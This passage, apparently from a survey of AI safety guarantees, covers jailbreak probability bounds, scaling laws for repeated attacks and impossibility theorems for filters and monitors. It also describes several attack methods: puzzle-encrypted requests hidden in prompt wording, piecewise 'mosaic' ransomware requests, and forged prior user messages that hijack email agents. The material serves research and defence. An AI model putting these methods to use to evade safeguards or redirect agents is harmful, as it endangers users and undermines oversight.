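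Lumos can also combine sampling over prompts with exact bounds for each prompt. In one experiment, Chaudhary and colleagues placed random mixtures of jailbreak instructions in front of ten requests for a person's email address. They sampled 50 mixtures per request and had BEAVER bound the probability that the model would keep the address private. Lumos then averaged the lower bounds and the upper bounds separately and widened the result to allow for sampling error. In the standard form of the method it uses, the margin on each side is

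$$\sqrt{\frac{2V\ln(2/\delta)}{n}} + \frac{7\ln(2/\delta)}{3(n-1)},$$

where $V$ is the variance of the sampled values and $\delta$ is the permitted chance of error. With $n = 50$ and $\delta = 0.025$, the second term alone is about 0.21, so the interval would be wide even if BEAVER found the exact probability for every prompt.

Averaged over the ten requests, the interval for the probability of a leak was 10% to 61% for Llama 3.2 3B and 24% to 48% for Qwen3 4B. When Chaudhary and colleagues sampled one reply per prompt with the default settings, the interval was 1% to 6% for both models. They explain that this test reflects only the default way of choosing tokens. The lower figures are more relevant to an operator who uses the default settings, and the higher ones to an operator who lets users change them.

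Suresh and colleagues ran a similar experiment with one request. BEAVER proved a leak probability of at least 10% for 29 of 50 sampled jailbreak texts on Llama 3.2 3B, which gives an interval of 43% to 72% for the probability of sampling such a text. They add that if the distribution contained ten billion texts, at least 4.3 billion would be risky. That follows only if all the texts are equally likely, because otherwise a few common ones could account for most of the 43%.

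### The effect of repeated attempts

An attacker who fails can try again. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability $v$, the chance of at least one success in $k$ attempts is

$$1 - (1-v)^k.$$

If each attempt has a 1 in 10,000 chance of producing a harmful output, the chance of at least one harmful output in 10,000 independent attempts is about 63%. To keep that chance below 1%, the operator needs a bound of about one in a million per attempt. Even if the attempts aren't independent, the chance is never more than $kv$, where $k$ is the number of attempts and $v$ is the bound for each attempt. BEAVER's 10% threshold for a risky prompt is far too high, since an attacker with a 10% chance per attempt would have a better than even chance of success after seven independent attempts.

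The formula applies to one prompt or to prompts with the same success rate. Suppose instead that half of all harmful requests succeed on 1% of attempts and the other half never do. The average rate is 0.5%, for which the formula predicts 99.3% success after 1,000 attempts, but attackers would succeed with almost all of the first half and none of the second, or about 50% overall. In general, using the average rate in the formula overstates the average success across requests after repeated independent attempts, but it can badly understate the risk for a particular request.

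*Best-of-N Jailbreaking* (2024) studied attacks that send many randomly altered versions of a request. The average success rate $S_N$ after $N$ attempts roughly followed a power law, $-\log S_N = aN^{-b}$, so it approached 100% much more slowly than it would if every attempt had the same chance of success. Curves fitted to 1,000 attempts predicted the success rate after 10,000 with an average error of 4.4 percentage points. *How Do Large Language Monkeys Get Their Power (Laws)?* (2025) explains why such laws arise both for jailbreaks and for mathematical problems. The success rate for each request approaches 100% exponentially, but an average over requests with very different success rates can follow a power law.

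*Statistical Estimation of Adversarial Risk in Large Language Models under Best-of-N Sampling* (2026) uses this to predict the results of large attacks from small tests. It assumes that success rates vary between requests according to a Beta distribution, a flexible family of curves between 0 and 1. One simulation uses parameters 0.4 and 4, which give an average success rate of 9%. A request with exactly that rate would almost certainly succeed at least once in 1,000 attempts, yet on average about 11% of requests would still not have succeeded. The paper warns that the fitted parameters may change with a different set of requests.

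Halder, Banerjee and Pehlevan (2026), in *Jailbreak Scaling Laws for Large Language Models*, a study from Harvard, ask what happens when the attacker also adds an adversarial string to the request. They call this prompt injection, but the attacker is the user, so it is a jailbreak. Let $p$ be the probability that a single reply is safe, which varies between requests. The attacker fails $k$ times with average probability $\mathbb{E}[p^k]$, and for large $k$ this depends almost entirely on the safest requests. If some requests are arbitrarily close to perfectly safe, the failure rate falls as a power of $k$. If no request is safer than some $\hat p < 1$, the rate also has a factor of $\hat p^{\,k}$ and falls exponentially:

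$$\mathbb{E}[p^k] \approx C\,k^{-\nu}\,\hat p^{\,k}.$$

For example, if $p$ is spread evenly between 0 and 1, the average of $p^k$ is $1/(k+1)$, so there is a 1% chance that all 99 of an attacker's first 99 attempts fail. That chance drops to about three in ten million if $p$ is spread evenly between 0 and 0.9.

In the experiments, strings from the automated attacks GCG and AutoDAN changed growth from the slow pattern to the fast one on several open Llama and OLMo models. With GCG, the upper limit $\hat p$ for Llama 3.2 3B was about 0.9. A stronger OpenAI model kept to the slow pattern under attack, which Halder and colleagues attribute to the strength of its safety training relative to the attack. They tested strings meant to work on many requests and models, so attacks tailored to one model could succeed faster. They also derive both patterns from a physical model of disordered magnets,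 in which the adversarial string acts as a magnetic field that pulls the output towards unsafe text.

*Escaping Alignment* (2026) disputes parts of this account. It finds no clean power law and argues that the change to exponential growth may come from the limited number of requests in the test sets. If the safest request in a set of 100 has a failure rate above zero, the average must eventually follow that request's exponential curve. A larger set would probably include safer requests and delay the change. The disagreement matters for predictions about very long attacks, because the fitted curves can differ greatly beyond the range of the data, and none of them is a proved upper bound.

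## Which guarantees are provably impossible?

Many of the bounds described so far are weak or narrow because nobody has found better ones. Several recent theorems prove that other guarantees are impossible. Each theorem depends on an assumption, for example that outputs can be arbitrarily long, that the filter has less computing time than the model, that training leaves some harmful behaviour in place, or that an agent can't check what it is told. If an operator can make that assumption false, the theorem no longer rules out the guarantee.

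### Perfect filters for outputs of any length

A perfect output filter blocks every forbidden output and lets every permitted one through. *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) proves that if a model can produce any finite text, a perfect filter exists exactly when the policy is decidable, meaning that some program can always determine in finite time whether a given text is forbidden.

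If the policy is decidable, the deciding program can serve as the filter. Conversely, suppose we have a perfect filter and want to know whether a text $w$ is forbidden. We try every combination of a prompt and the model's possible random choices in a fixed order until one produces $w$. The search must end, because the model can produce any text. We then run the filter on $w$ and the prompt we found, and its output is the answer.

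If a policy is undecidable, every filter for it makes infinitely many errors, because a filter with finitely many errors could be combined with a list of corrections to decide the policy. A filter that blocks every forbidden output therefore also blocks infinitely many permitted ones. Randomness doesn't help, because every randomised filter gives the wrong verdict on some output at least half the time.

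A filter can always detect banned phrases, but no filter can correctly decide, for every program, whether running it would delete the user's files. This follows from the halting problem. Alan Turing showed in the 1930s that no program can determine, for every program, whether it eventually stops. If one could, we could write a program that runs it on itself and then does the opposite of what it predicts. For any program $M$, the program "simulate $M$, then delete the files" deletes the files exactly when $M$ stops, so a perfect filter for file-deleting programs would solve the halting problem. *LLM Censorship* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2023) reached the same conclusion for outputs that describe programs, using Rice's theorem, which extends Turing's result to every non-trivial question about what programs compute.

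These results apply more directly to code than to advice. Amer and colleagues can extend theirs to text that does harm through its reader only by assuming that the reader can carry out any program exactly, with unlimited time and memory. They note that this is not a theorem about persuasion. Limiting output length also removes the undecidability, because the set of forbidden texts is then finite and can in principle be listed. A perfect filter therefore exists for each length limit, although no single program can construct the right filter for every limit.

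### Replies in code

Glukhov and colleagues also prove that a filter for outputs of limited length must permit everything or nothing if three conditions hold. First, the model can apply any reversible code the user describes, such as moving every letter three places along the alphabet. Second, the filter doesn't know which codes the user can undo. Third, the filter must treat an encoded version of a forbidden text as forbidden if the user can decode it.

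To see why, suppose the filter permits a text $x$ and forbids a text $y$. Some reversible code turns $y$ into $x$. If the user knows that code, the harmless-looking reply $x$ may be an encoding of $y$, so the filter must forbid $x$ too. The same argument applies to every permitted text.

This is consistent with the perfect filters that exist for bounded outputs, because those filters enforce a fixed list of forbidden texts. Here, whether a text is forbidden depends on what its reader can decode.

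Attackers cannot exploit the full strength of this conclusion. It is hard to choose a code that turns a particular forbidden text into a particular harmless one without already knowing the forbidden text, and the model reveals nothing to an attacker who already knows it. Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that real attackers would need a code that works without such knowledge. Ordinary encryption does, but its output looks like gibberish, which a filter can block, though this also blocks some harmless replies. Codes that produce natural-looking text are harder to catch.

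Even a filter that judges every reply correctly can fail if the user asks for the parts of something harmful separately. Glukhov and colleagues call this a mosaic prompt and give the example of ransomware, which locks a victim's files until the victim pays. A user could request each function of the ransomware in a separate conversation, and each function would be harmless on its own. The user has to know how to combine them, though the model may supply that knowledge too.

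### Confirming violations but not compliance

A monitor that watches a program's actions has an easier task than a filter that reads the program's text. Amer and colleagues prove that a monitor can stop exactly the forbidden runs if and only if a program can decide which finite traces are forbidden. This matches Ray's result on gates for tool calls. To enforce the rule "never delete a file", the monitor only has to block each deletion. But if the rule forbids delivering certain texts, the monitor must judge each text before sending it, so the theorem about filters applies again.

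Some operators want a verdict before a program runs. *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) studies a gatekeeper who reads programs written by an AI assistant and may run them for as long as necessary. A category of programs is confirmable if some procedure eventually outputs "yes" for every program in it and never for any other. The procedure may run forever on programs outside the category.

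| Rule | Are violations confirmable? | Is compliance confirmable? |
|---|---|---|
| Never perform a forbidden action | yes | no |
| Publish the same output whatever a secret is | no | no |
| Eventually answer every request | no | no |
| Any of these, judged on the first $T$ steps only | yes | yes |

The gatekeeper can confirm that a program performs the forbidden action by running it until it does, but no procedure can confirm every safe program. The program "simulate $M$, then perform the forbidden action" is safe exactly when $M$ never stops, so a procedure that confirmed every safe program could also confirm that $M$ never stops whenever that is true. Running $M$ confirms the cases where it does stop, so the two methods together would solve the halting problem.

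Short, readable programs can cause this difficulty. One of Pérez-Acle's examples checks the even numbers from 4 upwards and performs the forbidden action if it finds one that isn't the sum of two primes. Certifying this program as safe would prove Goldbach's conjecture, which says that no such number exists.

Leaks are harder to confirm than forbidden actions. Suppose a program publishes a number when the secret is 0 and has so far published nothing when the secret is 1. The gatekeeper can't determine whether the second run is just slower or will stay silent, which would be a leak. A finite record also can't show that the rule about answering requests has been kept, because it doesn't cover all future requests, or that the rule has been broken, because an unanswered request might still get an answer.

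No reliable certification procedure can certify every safe program. For any such procedure, we can write a program that searches for its own certificate and performs the forbidden action if it finds one. The procedure never certifies this program, so the program never performs the action and is safe. The program is only slightly longer than the code that checks the certificates.

### Time limits make questions decidable but not cheap

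Real computers have finite memory, and operators can stop a program after $T$ steps. It is decidable whether the program does anything forbidden in that time, because the gatekeeper can run it for $T$ steps in a sandbox, an isolated environment where it can do no damage.

No shortcut for checking programs is always right. Pérez-Acle constructs a program that runs the gatekeeper's check on its own code. If the verdict is "safe", the program performs the forbidden action, and otherwise it does nothing. Any verdict that arrives early enough for the program to act on it is therefore wrong. A gatekeeper that is right about every program must, in the worst case, take about as long as running the program for the full $T$ steps, allowing for simulation overhead. For programs with $m$ bits of memory and no time limit, the worst case grows like $2^m$ steps, which is far too many to run even when $m$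 is 100.

The same limits apply to containment. *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (2026) uses the halting problem to show that whether a sandbox is ever escaped is undecidable in general. If the possible escape paths can be put in a finite list, they can all be checked. The remaining risk is that the list doesn't match the deployed system.

Pérez-Acle also measured how often ordinary programs are unsafe and how often a short test misses them, using 2.2 million random programs of 4 to 24 instructions for a simple simulated machine. About 1.6% performed the forbidden action. A test that ran each program for 8 steps wrongly passed 30.2% of the unsafe programs with 24 instructions. That share fell to 2.9% with 16 steps and 0.2% with 32. With 128 steps or more, the test caught every unsafe program at all the lengths tested.

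For the rule about secrets, even a test of 4,096 steps wrongly rejected up to 0.37% of the compliant programs, depending on program length. The wrongly rejected programs all published the same endless sequence for both values of the secret, but at different speeds, so their outputs looked different no matter when the test stopped.

Programs written against a particular checker gave very different results. Pérez-Acle built one for each of eight checkers and eight time limits. The checker that ran programs for the full time was always right about the program written against it, and the seven faster checkers were always wrong about theirs. Random programs are therefore a poor guide to security, for the same reason that an average over a distribution of prompts is. They are also a poor model of the code that language models write, which may wait much longer before doing anything harmful.

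### Filters that are faster than the model

Operators usually want a filter that costs much less to run than the model it protects. Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, prove that for some models no such filter can reliably detect harmful prompts. The proof uses a time-lock puzzle, which is quick to create but slow to solve. The puzzle is to calculate

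$$r^{(2^t)} \bmod n,$$

where $n$ is the product of two large primes $p$ and $q$. The standard assumption is that anyone who doesn't know $p$ and $q$ has to square $r$ about $t$ times, one squaring after another, and that extra computers don't help. The person who chose $p$ and $q$ can first reduce the exponent $2^t$ to its remainder modulo $(p-1)(q-1)$, which makes the calculation fast.

The attack then works as follows:

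1. The attacker creates a puzzle, uses its solution as a key and encrypts a harmful request with it. With some extra processing, the puzzle and the encrypted request look like random bits.
2. The attacker writes an innocent prompt with a text generator that makes random choices, such as whether to begin with "Hello" or "Hi". The hidden bits determine these choices.
3. The model recovers the bits from the wording of the prompt, solves the puzzle, decrypts the request and carries it out.

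A filter that has much less time than it takes to solve the puzzle can't distinguish the hidden bits from random ones, so it can't distinguish the attacker's prompts from innocent prompts from the same generator. Such a filter can't let through nearly all of the innocent prompts without also letting through nearly all of the attacker's.

Step 3 is the weak point because ordinary models don't search a greeting's wording for hidden puzzles. Ball and colleagues admit that the model they construct behaves in a contrived way. Their theorem rules out a method that would produce a fast, reliable filter for every model, including an untrustworthy one, but it doesn't show that any existing model lacks such a filter. An attacker could openly ask an ordinary model with programming tools to solve a puzzle and follow the decrypted instructions, but that prompt wouldn't look innocent, and the filter could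 reject all prompts of this kind.

A filter as powerful as the model could solve the puzzle too, but it would take about as much compute to run, and the operator would need a reason to trust it. Suppose instead that the model and the attacker share a secret key, or that the attacker has a public key and the matching private key is built into the model. Under standard cryptographic assumptions, no filter fast enough to be practical can detect the hidden requests, even one more powerful than the model. This matters mainly if someone has tampered with the model or if the model itself helps attackers.

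Ball and colleagues prove a similar theorem for output filters, including filters with more computing time than the model. In their construction, the output contains a hidden puzzle, and the definition of harm involves solving it. An output can be harmful in this sense even though no efficient filter could recognise it. It is much less clear that instructions a person can read and use would be so hard to detect.

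### Can training remove the harmful behaviour?

Instead of adding a filter, developers can train the model itself to behave well. Wolf, Avnery and colleagues (2023), in *Fundamental Limitations of Alignment in Large Language Models*, argue that training which makes a behaviour rare without eliminating it leaves the model open to jailbreaks. They describe the model's text as a mixture of an ill-behaved component $P_-$, with a small weight $\alpha$, and a well-behaved component $P_+$:

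$$P = \alpha P_- + (1-\alpha) P_+.$$

A prompt $s$ changes the weights. By Bayes' rule, the new weight $\alpha'$ satisfies

$$\frac{\alpha'}{1-\alpha'} = \frac{\alpha}{1-\alpha}\cdot\frac{P_-(s)}{P_+(s)}.$$

The attacker writes a prompt in the style of the ill-behaved component. The main assumption is that each new sentence from $P_-$ raises the logarithm of the last fraction by more than some fixed $\beta > 0$ on average. After enough sentences, the ill-behaved component dominates the model's behavior.

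Suppose $\alpha$ is one in a million and $\beta = 1$. The attacker then needs about 19 sentences ($\ln 10^6 + \ln 99 \approx 18.4$, rounded up) to raise the weight of the ill-behaved component to 99%. Further training that makes $\alpha$ a thousand times smaller adds only seven sentences. Wolf and colleagues prove similar results for models with a protective opening prompt, for attacks spread over a conversation, and for systems that choose the best of several replies.

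The rare harmful replies that Nazeri and colleagues found suggest that the assumption that $\alpha$ is above zero is realistic. The assumption about $\beta$ is more doubtful, because it requires an ill-behaved component that remains distinct however long the prompt becomes. A model could, for example, write a harmful sentence with probability one in a million at every step, whatever the preceding text. Its harmful behaviour would have a positive probability, but no prompt could make it more likely. A developer could approach this ideal by training a model to return to good behaviour after reading bad text.

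Wolf and colleagues tested their account on models from the LLaMA family. Prompts built by their method made these models misbehave, and the models' outputs moved closer to those of an ill-behaved version as the prompts grew longer. This supports the mechanism for those models, which are old by now, but doesn't show that it must work on every later model.

### A theorem called "Jailbreak is unavoidable"

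*Mission Impossible* (Su, Kempe and Ullrich, 2024) uses a different argument, which splits a prompt into a concept, such as how to build a bomb, and a query, which is the wording around it. The attacker can change only the query. For a harmful concept, the model chooses among $n$ possible replies, some of them harmful. Safety training changes the replies' probabilities but doesn't remove the harmful ones. A jailbreak occurs when the harmful replies have a total probability of at least $p$. By assumption, the attacker can move the model's output distribution a distance $\varepsilon$ towards the harmful region.

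The proof considers all possible probability distributions over the $n$ replies. If 2% of the replies are harmful, a distribution chosen at random gives them about 2% of the probability. With a threshold of $p = 1\%$ and a large $n$, nearly all distributions therefore count as jailbroken, and still more do once the attacker can shift them by $\varepsilon$. The theorem states that a jailbreak exists with probability at least

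$$1 - \gamma_s\,\big(1 - \Phi(a_\varepsilon)\big).$$

Here $\Phi$ is the cumulative normal distribution, and $a_\varepsilon$ grows with $\varepsilon$ and with the number of harmful replies. The factor $\gamma_s$ measures how strongly training, compared with random choice, concentrates models in the region that the attacker can't reach.

The result depends heavily on $\gamma_s$, because safety training is meant to make the model's distribution far from random. If $1 - \Phi(a_\varepsilon)$ is one in a million and training makes some safe distributions a million times as likely as they would be by chance, the lower bound falls to zero. Su and colleagues state that their result applies as long as training has not concentrated the model in an "extremely safe area", a condition that the theorem's title omits. The assumption about $\varepsilon$ also presupposes much of the conclusion, because the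 main question about jailbreaks is whether rewording can move a well-trained model towards harmful replies.

The assumption that harmful replies survive training is better supported. One explanation, from Su and colleagues, is that a common training method penalises a model for departing from an earlier version of itself, which gave harmful replies. For harmful prompts, they instead penalised departures from the earlier version's response to the same prompt preceded by a safety reminder. This lowered the average attack success rate from 42.0% to 37.0% on HarmBench and from 28.4% to 20.9% on 100 AdvBench prompts. The reduction is useful but modest, and it shows that developers have some control over a quantity the theorem treats as given.

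### Rewriting prompts without sudden jumps

Some defences rewrite suspicious prompts before the model reads them. *The Defense Trilemma* (Bhatt, Munshi and colleagues, 2026) proves that no rewriting function can simultaneously be continuous (similar prompts get similar rewrites), leave all safe prompts unchanged and bring every response's unsafety score below the safety threshold. The proof assumes that the score varies continuously with the prompt and that the space of prompts is connected, so that a path without gaps leads from safe to unsafe prompts.

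The proof uses safe prompts that converge to a prompt whose score is exactly at the threshold. $D$ leaves each safe prompt unchanged, so by continuity it also leaves the limit unchanged and fails to bring its score below the threshold. If the score also rises steeply enough beyond that point, a region of prompts remains unsafe after rewriting.

The proof is machine-checked in Lean, but its assumptions don't fit text well. Prompts are discrete strings, and a filter that replaces every unsafe prompt with a fixed refusal makes the kind of jump the theorem excludes. Bhatt and colleagues also prove a version for finite sets of prompts, in which a complete defence must sometimes turn two different prompts into the same one, as a standard refusal is meant to do. They acknowledge that blocklists, output filters and safety training lie outside the theorem.

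### Claims that an agent can't check

Prompt injections don't have to contain instructions. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) gives the example of an email that requests a travel refund and says that the department head has approved it. The right action depends on whether this is true. A defence that ignores all claims in emails would also ignore genuine approvals.

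Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian's argument draws on contextual integrity, Helen Nissenbaum's theory of privacy. In this theory, whether a flow of information is appropriate depends on its sender, its receiver, the person it concerns, the type of information and the conditions under which it is shared. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian extend this to an agent's actions. An attacker can invent a false fact about any of these factors, such as a forged permission, that would make the action appropriate if it were true.

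The theorem behind the argument is short. Suppose that an action is appropriate in one situation and inappropriate in another, and that an attacker can make the second look exactly like the first to the agent. The agent then has to act with the same probability $\pi$ in both, so

$$\underbrace{\pi}_{\text{attack succeeds}} + \underbrace{(1-\pi)}_{\text{legitimate request blocked}} = 1.$$

At least one of the two error rates is 50% or more. This applies to any decision-maker, including a person, and greater intelligence doesn't help if the available evidence is the same.

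The theorem doesn't prove that such a pair of situations exists in every deployment. An agent can tell the two situations apart if it can verify approvals. The department head could sign them cryptographically, or the agent could look them up in a system that outsiders can't edit. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian accept this but argue that each check covers only some claims, while attackers can keep inventing new claims. They expect the problem to grow as agents act more independently.

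In their experiments, current agents judged such claims badly. A user asked an email assistant only for a summary, and Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrote emails designed to make the assistant send a reply. The attacker could revise each email up to 15 times in each of three parallel runs. It succeeded in 96.7% of 150 scenarios, compared with 0.67% for unrevised emails. The most common trick was to forge an earlier message from the user and quote it in the thread. The best emails also worked unchanged on other models, in 63.3% of cases on GPT-5.4 and 92.6% on Gemini 3 Pro.

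These attacks did not depend on the ambiguity in the theorem. The user had not asked for any reply, and ordinary software can track which text came from the user. A monitor that withheld the email tool until the user asked for a message would have blocked every attack, but also replies that a genuine policy allowed. The agent was also instructed to send appropriate messages without asking the user first.

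Clear limits also helped in a test without an attacker, in which a colleague's email combined an authorised request with an unauthorised one. GPT-5.2 carried out the unauthorised request in 65% of scenarios, GPT-5.4 in 34% and Claude in 6%. When the user said that messages to outsiders needed approval, the rate fell to 12% for GPT-5.2 and to zero for the other two.

### Guarantees that survive the theorems

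The theorems about undecidable policies do not set a minimum for a filter's average error. Amer and colleagues show that, for any distribution of outputs and any $\delta > 0$, some filter blocks everything forbidden and blocks a permitted output with probability below $\delta$. The filter allows a finite list of permitted texts that covers nearly all the permitted outputs likely to occur, and blocks everything else. No general procedure can compile such lists for an undecidable policy, but people may be able to prove particular cases.

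A low average error does not protect a filter against attackers. If a share $a$ of uses are attacks, each attack gets a forbidden output past the filter with probability $\sigma$, and each success causes a loss of at least $\lambda$, then the expected loss per use is at least $a\sigma\lambda$, however accurate the filter is on ordinary outputs.

A filter that blocks everything forbidden has $\sigma = 0$, even if it also blocks many harmless outputs. Pérez-Acle describes exactly when such a filter can still do its job. Let $P$ be the set of permitted programs and $O$ the smaller set that the gatekeeper is obliged to admit. The gatekeeper needs a set $A$ with

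$$O \subseteq A \subseteq P$$

whose membership a program can decide. $A$ can omit any permitted program outside $O$. The verifier for eBPF, a system for adding small programs to an operating system's core, works this way. It admits only programs that it can prove safe and rejects some safe ones.

This can exclude many safe machines. Pérez-Acle classified every possible machine with three, four or five states in a simple model. A rule that admits only machines with no forbidden action anywhere in them accepted 71.9% of the safe three-state machines but only 47.3% of the safe five-state ones. The safe machines it rejected contained the forbidden action but never reached it. Amer and colleagues add that over-blocking can itself be dangerous, for example if a filter withholds a warning or a remedy.

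Rules about observable actions avoid much of this problem, because a monitor can let a program run and stop only the forbidden action. Dongol's fence, which permanently revokes tools at the first untrusted read, remains secure even if the agent runs forever. But an agent that handles successive requests needs its tools back for each new one, which the theorem doesn't allow. If an injection can supply a whole program instead of a single call, the fence is enough only inside a sandbox.

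## What is left of a guarantee in a deployed system?

The email assistant described earlier comes with a proof that it never sends a message to an unapproved address after reading untrusted text. The proof is about a game with six states and one outside address. If a company builds the assistant into a product, with real mailboxes and a language model that it replaces every few months, the proof remains valid but protects users only as long as the product matches the game. That requires a rule that matches what the company intended, a monitor that every action passes through, correct labels, and users who understand what they approve. These conditions must still hold after each update.

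### One rule on its way into a product

The company presumably wants to stop strangers from accessing users' data or acting in users' names, but the rule only covers messages. An assistant can give a stranger the same information without sending a message, by sharing a folder or opening a web address that contains a password reset code.

A message to an approved address can also do harm. The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved* describes an attack that OpenAI's automated attacker discovered against the agent in the company's browser, ChatGPT Atlas. An email in the user's inbox contained hidden instructions to send a resignation letter to the user's CEO. When the user later asked for an out-of-office message, the agent came across this email and resigned on the user's behalf. The CEO's address would be on almost any approved list, so the rule would have allowed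 the letter.

The Atlas agent is hard to monitor because it works through clicks and keystrokes. It sends a message from a webmail page by clicking, so a monitor that checks for calls to a "send" tool would miss it. The monitor would have to infer what each click does from the page, part of which strangers may have written. The company can avoid this by giving the assistant a mail tool and no browser. An agent with a command line needs similar restrictions, because a command line offers many ways to send a message.

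Red Hat's *Beyond guardrails* (2026) describes a scheme with three risk labels: untrusted input, access to sensitive systems, and the ability to change or send out data. No agent or tool may have more than two. An assistant that reads strangers' emails, searches the mailbox and sends replies has all three, so the scheme would require splitting it up. Red Hat warns that people can tamper with input that was once trustworthy, and that the scheme helps only if every label is correct and the software enforces the separation. A developer who labels incoming email as untrusted can easily forget to do the same for a contact's display name, which the contact chose, or for notes that the assistant saved last week after reading a stranger's email.

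In the game, the user either approves an address or doesn't, but in a deployed product the user approves through a confirmation box that they may read for only two seconds. It also matters whether the model or fixed code writes the text in that box. *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (Hong, She and colleagues, 2026) includes confirmation by fixed code among its methods for enforcing rules. Fixed code can show the real address and message, so a hijacked model can't misdescribe them, though users may still approve without reading.

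Replacing the language model doesn't affect the proof, which already allows the model to propose anything, but adding a tool can invalidate the guarantee. If a developer gives the assistant a "share link" function and the monitor lets unfamiliar calls through, the assistant can send data out in a way the game doesn't include. A monitor that blocks every tool not on its list would preserve the guarantee, but the new function wouldn't work until somebody extended the proof to cover it.

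Protections that come from training can weaken with any new model. *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*, thezvi's commentary on the safety document for two OpenAI models released in November 2026, quotes the company as saying it adjusted both models' refusal boundaries "after observing regressions in jailbreak resistance". According to the commentary, the adjustment only partly solved the problem.

### Who writes the rules, and how well

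Someone has to write the rules before software can enforce them. Hong and colleagues examined 80 benchmarks of agent safety or security and found that 49 gave the agent no safety rules, while 19 stated only goals, such as refusing "anything unsafe", without defining the terms. Only seven had rules precise enough to check. Five of these seven applied their rules to every task, and all five were for agents with a fixed job, such as changing airline bookings. Hong and colleagues caution that benchmarks may reflect researchers' interests more than companies' needs.

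They then went through the rules for three agents sentence by sentence. The first two were an airline's customer-service agent from τ²-bench and a car's voice assistant from CAR-bench. The third, an assistant for medical records from MedAgentBench, had no safety rules, so GPT-5.2 wrote 50. An automated hazard analysis suggested 5,138 more, from which the researchers sampled and condensed another 38. After discarding sentences that were not requirements on the agent, they judged that ordinary program code could enforce 42 of 51 rules for the airline, 17 of 18 for the car and 34 of 57 for the medical assistant, or 74% overall.

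Nearly all of these 93 rules need only a simple check. The software compares an argument with a database, restricts the format of a call, asks the user a fixed question or displays a fixed text. Only five rules need temporal logic or information-flow control, which suggests that many companies could enforce most of their rules without either method. But the attackers in these benchmarks are mostly users who ask for things the policy forbids. A study of agents that read strangers' emails would probably have found more rules that depend on whether the agent has read untrusted text, and enforcing those rules requires software that tracks this.

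The rules that code couldn't enforce were about tone, made-up information, the order of steps in a conversation, or common sense. One airline rule forbids the agent from offering compensation unless the customer explicitly asks for it, and deciding what counts as asking requires interpreting the customer's language. Hong and colleagues suggest a cruder rule that blocks the compensation tools until the customer's reply is exactly the word "compensation". Software can enforce this rule perfectly, but a customer who writes "I'd like something for the trouble" gets no compensation, and anyone who knows the word can unlock the tools.

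The researchers ran the agents with and without the checks. The agents had the full policy in their instructions in both cases.

| Agent and model | Runs that broke an enforceable rule, no checks | Tasks solved, no checks | Tasks solved, with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Airline, GPT-4o | 52% | 36% | 48% |
| Airline, GPT-5 | 20% | 68% | 70% |
| Car, GPT-5 | 21% | 59% | 72% |
| Medical records, GPT-5 | 23% | 59% | 67% |
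| Medical records with hostile users, GPT-5 | 62% | not measured | not measured |

With the checks on, no run broke an enforceable rule, because the checks reject every call that would. The share of solved tasks also rose in every comparison. The gains for the airline may be due to chance, but those for the car and the medical records are statistically significant. Hong and colleagues think the error messages help, because an agent that learns why a call was wrong can try something else instead of finishing with a bad result.

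Some of the checks look better suited to honest mistakes than to attacks. The airline's original tool for cancelling a ticket takes only a ticket number. The checked version also takes a user ID and compares it with the ticket's owner, but the agent fills in that ID, so an agent under an attacker's control could supply the owner's. To stop this, the software would have to take the ID from the customer's login.

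Using a language model to write the rules also caused problems. The researchers threw out some of the medical rules because they contained made-up requirements that made no sense with the available tools. They also left ten enforceable rules unimplemented because these required expert knowledge, such as the right dosage units for each medicine. A company can therefore use a model to draft its policy, but it still needs experts in the field to check the draft.

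A vending machine run by an AI agent shows what happens when such rules are missing. According to The Hacker News' *OpenAI’s GPT-Red Automates Prompt Injection Testing to Harden GPT-5.6 Sol* (2026), OpenAI aimed its automated attacker GPT-Red at a machine built by Andon Labs. GPT-Red got the agent to cut the price of an expensive item to $0.50, order a new $100 item for the same price and cancel another customer's order. Checking that the order belonged to the logged-in customer would have prevented the cancellation. The price cut broke no rule, because $0.50 was the lowest price allowed. A minimum based on each item's cost would have served the owner better.

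### Amazon's automated-reasoning checks

Amazon sells a product based on formal logic. AWS's *Automated Reasoning checks is now available in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* (2025), an announcement from Amazon's cloud division, promised "mathematically rigorous guarantees" that a model's replies follow a customer's business rules. The process has four steps:

1. The customer uploads a document, such as a company's rules on parental leave. Software that uses language models turns it into variables and logical rules.
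2. The customer reviews these rules and tests them on sample questions and answers.
3. When the chatbot replies to a user, a language model translates the conversation into values for the variables.
4. The system checks by logic whether those values are consistent with the rules, and reports which rules support or contradict the reply.

The mathematical rigour is in the last step. AWS's documentation, *What are Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails?*, lists "No prompt injection protection" as the first limitation, because the system checks whatever text it receives, including text that an attacker has manipulated. The system also only reports its findings, so a bad reply still reaches the user unless the customer's own application withholds it.

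A verdict of "valid" covers only what the variables capture, so the gap between text and propositions remains. AWS, which makes the system, gives the example of a student who writes, "I can submit my homework late because I have a fake doctor's note". If the policy has a variable for having a doctor's note but none for whether the note is genuine, the system may return "valid".

Mistakes can occur when the document is translated into rules or when the conversation is translated into values. AWS produces a report that scores how well the rules cover the document and links each rule to the sentence it came from. It offers tests for the values and warns that accuracy depends partly on how well the customer describes each variable. The documentation gives no general error rate for either translation, so customers have to measure it on their own policies. In June 2026, AWS's *Automated Reasoning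 checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails add new policy refinement workflows* (2026) announced tools that reduce the manual work of improving a policy. But a policy refined until it passes a set of tests may still fail on questions that nobody thought to test.

AWS refers customers to its content filters for protection against prompt injection. *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails announces a new API targeting agentic AI workflows* (2026) describes an API that lets developers check separately for jailbreaks, prompt injections and attempts to extract a model's instructions. These checks are detectors, so a company that uses both products has no proofs about attackers, even though it has logical proofs about its leave policy.

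### Rates that laboratories publish

Developers publish test results for the models themselves. The table shows how much Anthropic's prompt injection figures depend on the setting and on what the rate measures.

| Model | Setting | What the rate counts | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Browser, with safeguards | Single attempts by an adaptive attacker | 1.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Restricted coding environment | Successes in 200 attempts | 0% |
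| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, without safeguards | Success at the first attempt | 17.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, with safeguards | Success by the 200th attempt | 57.1% |
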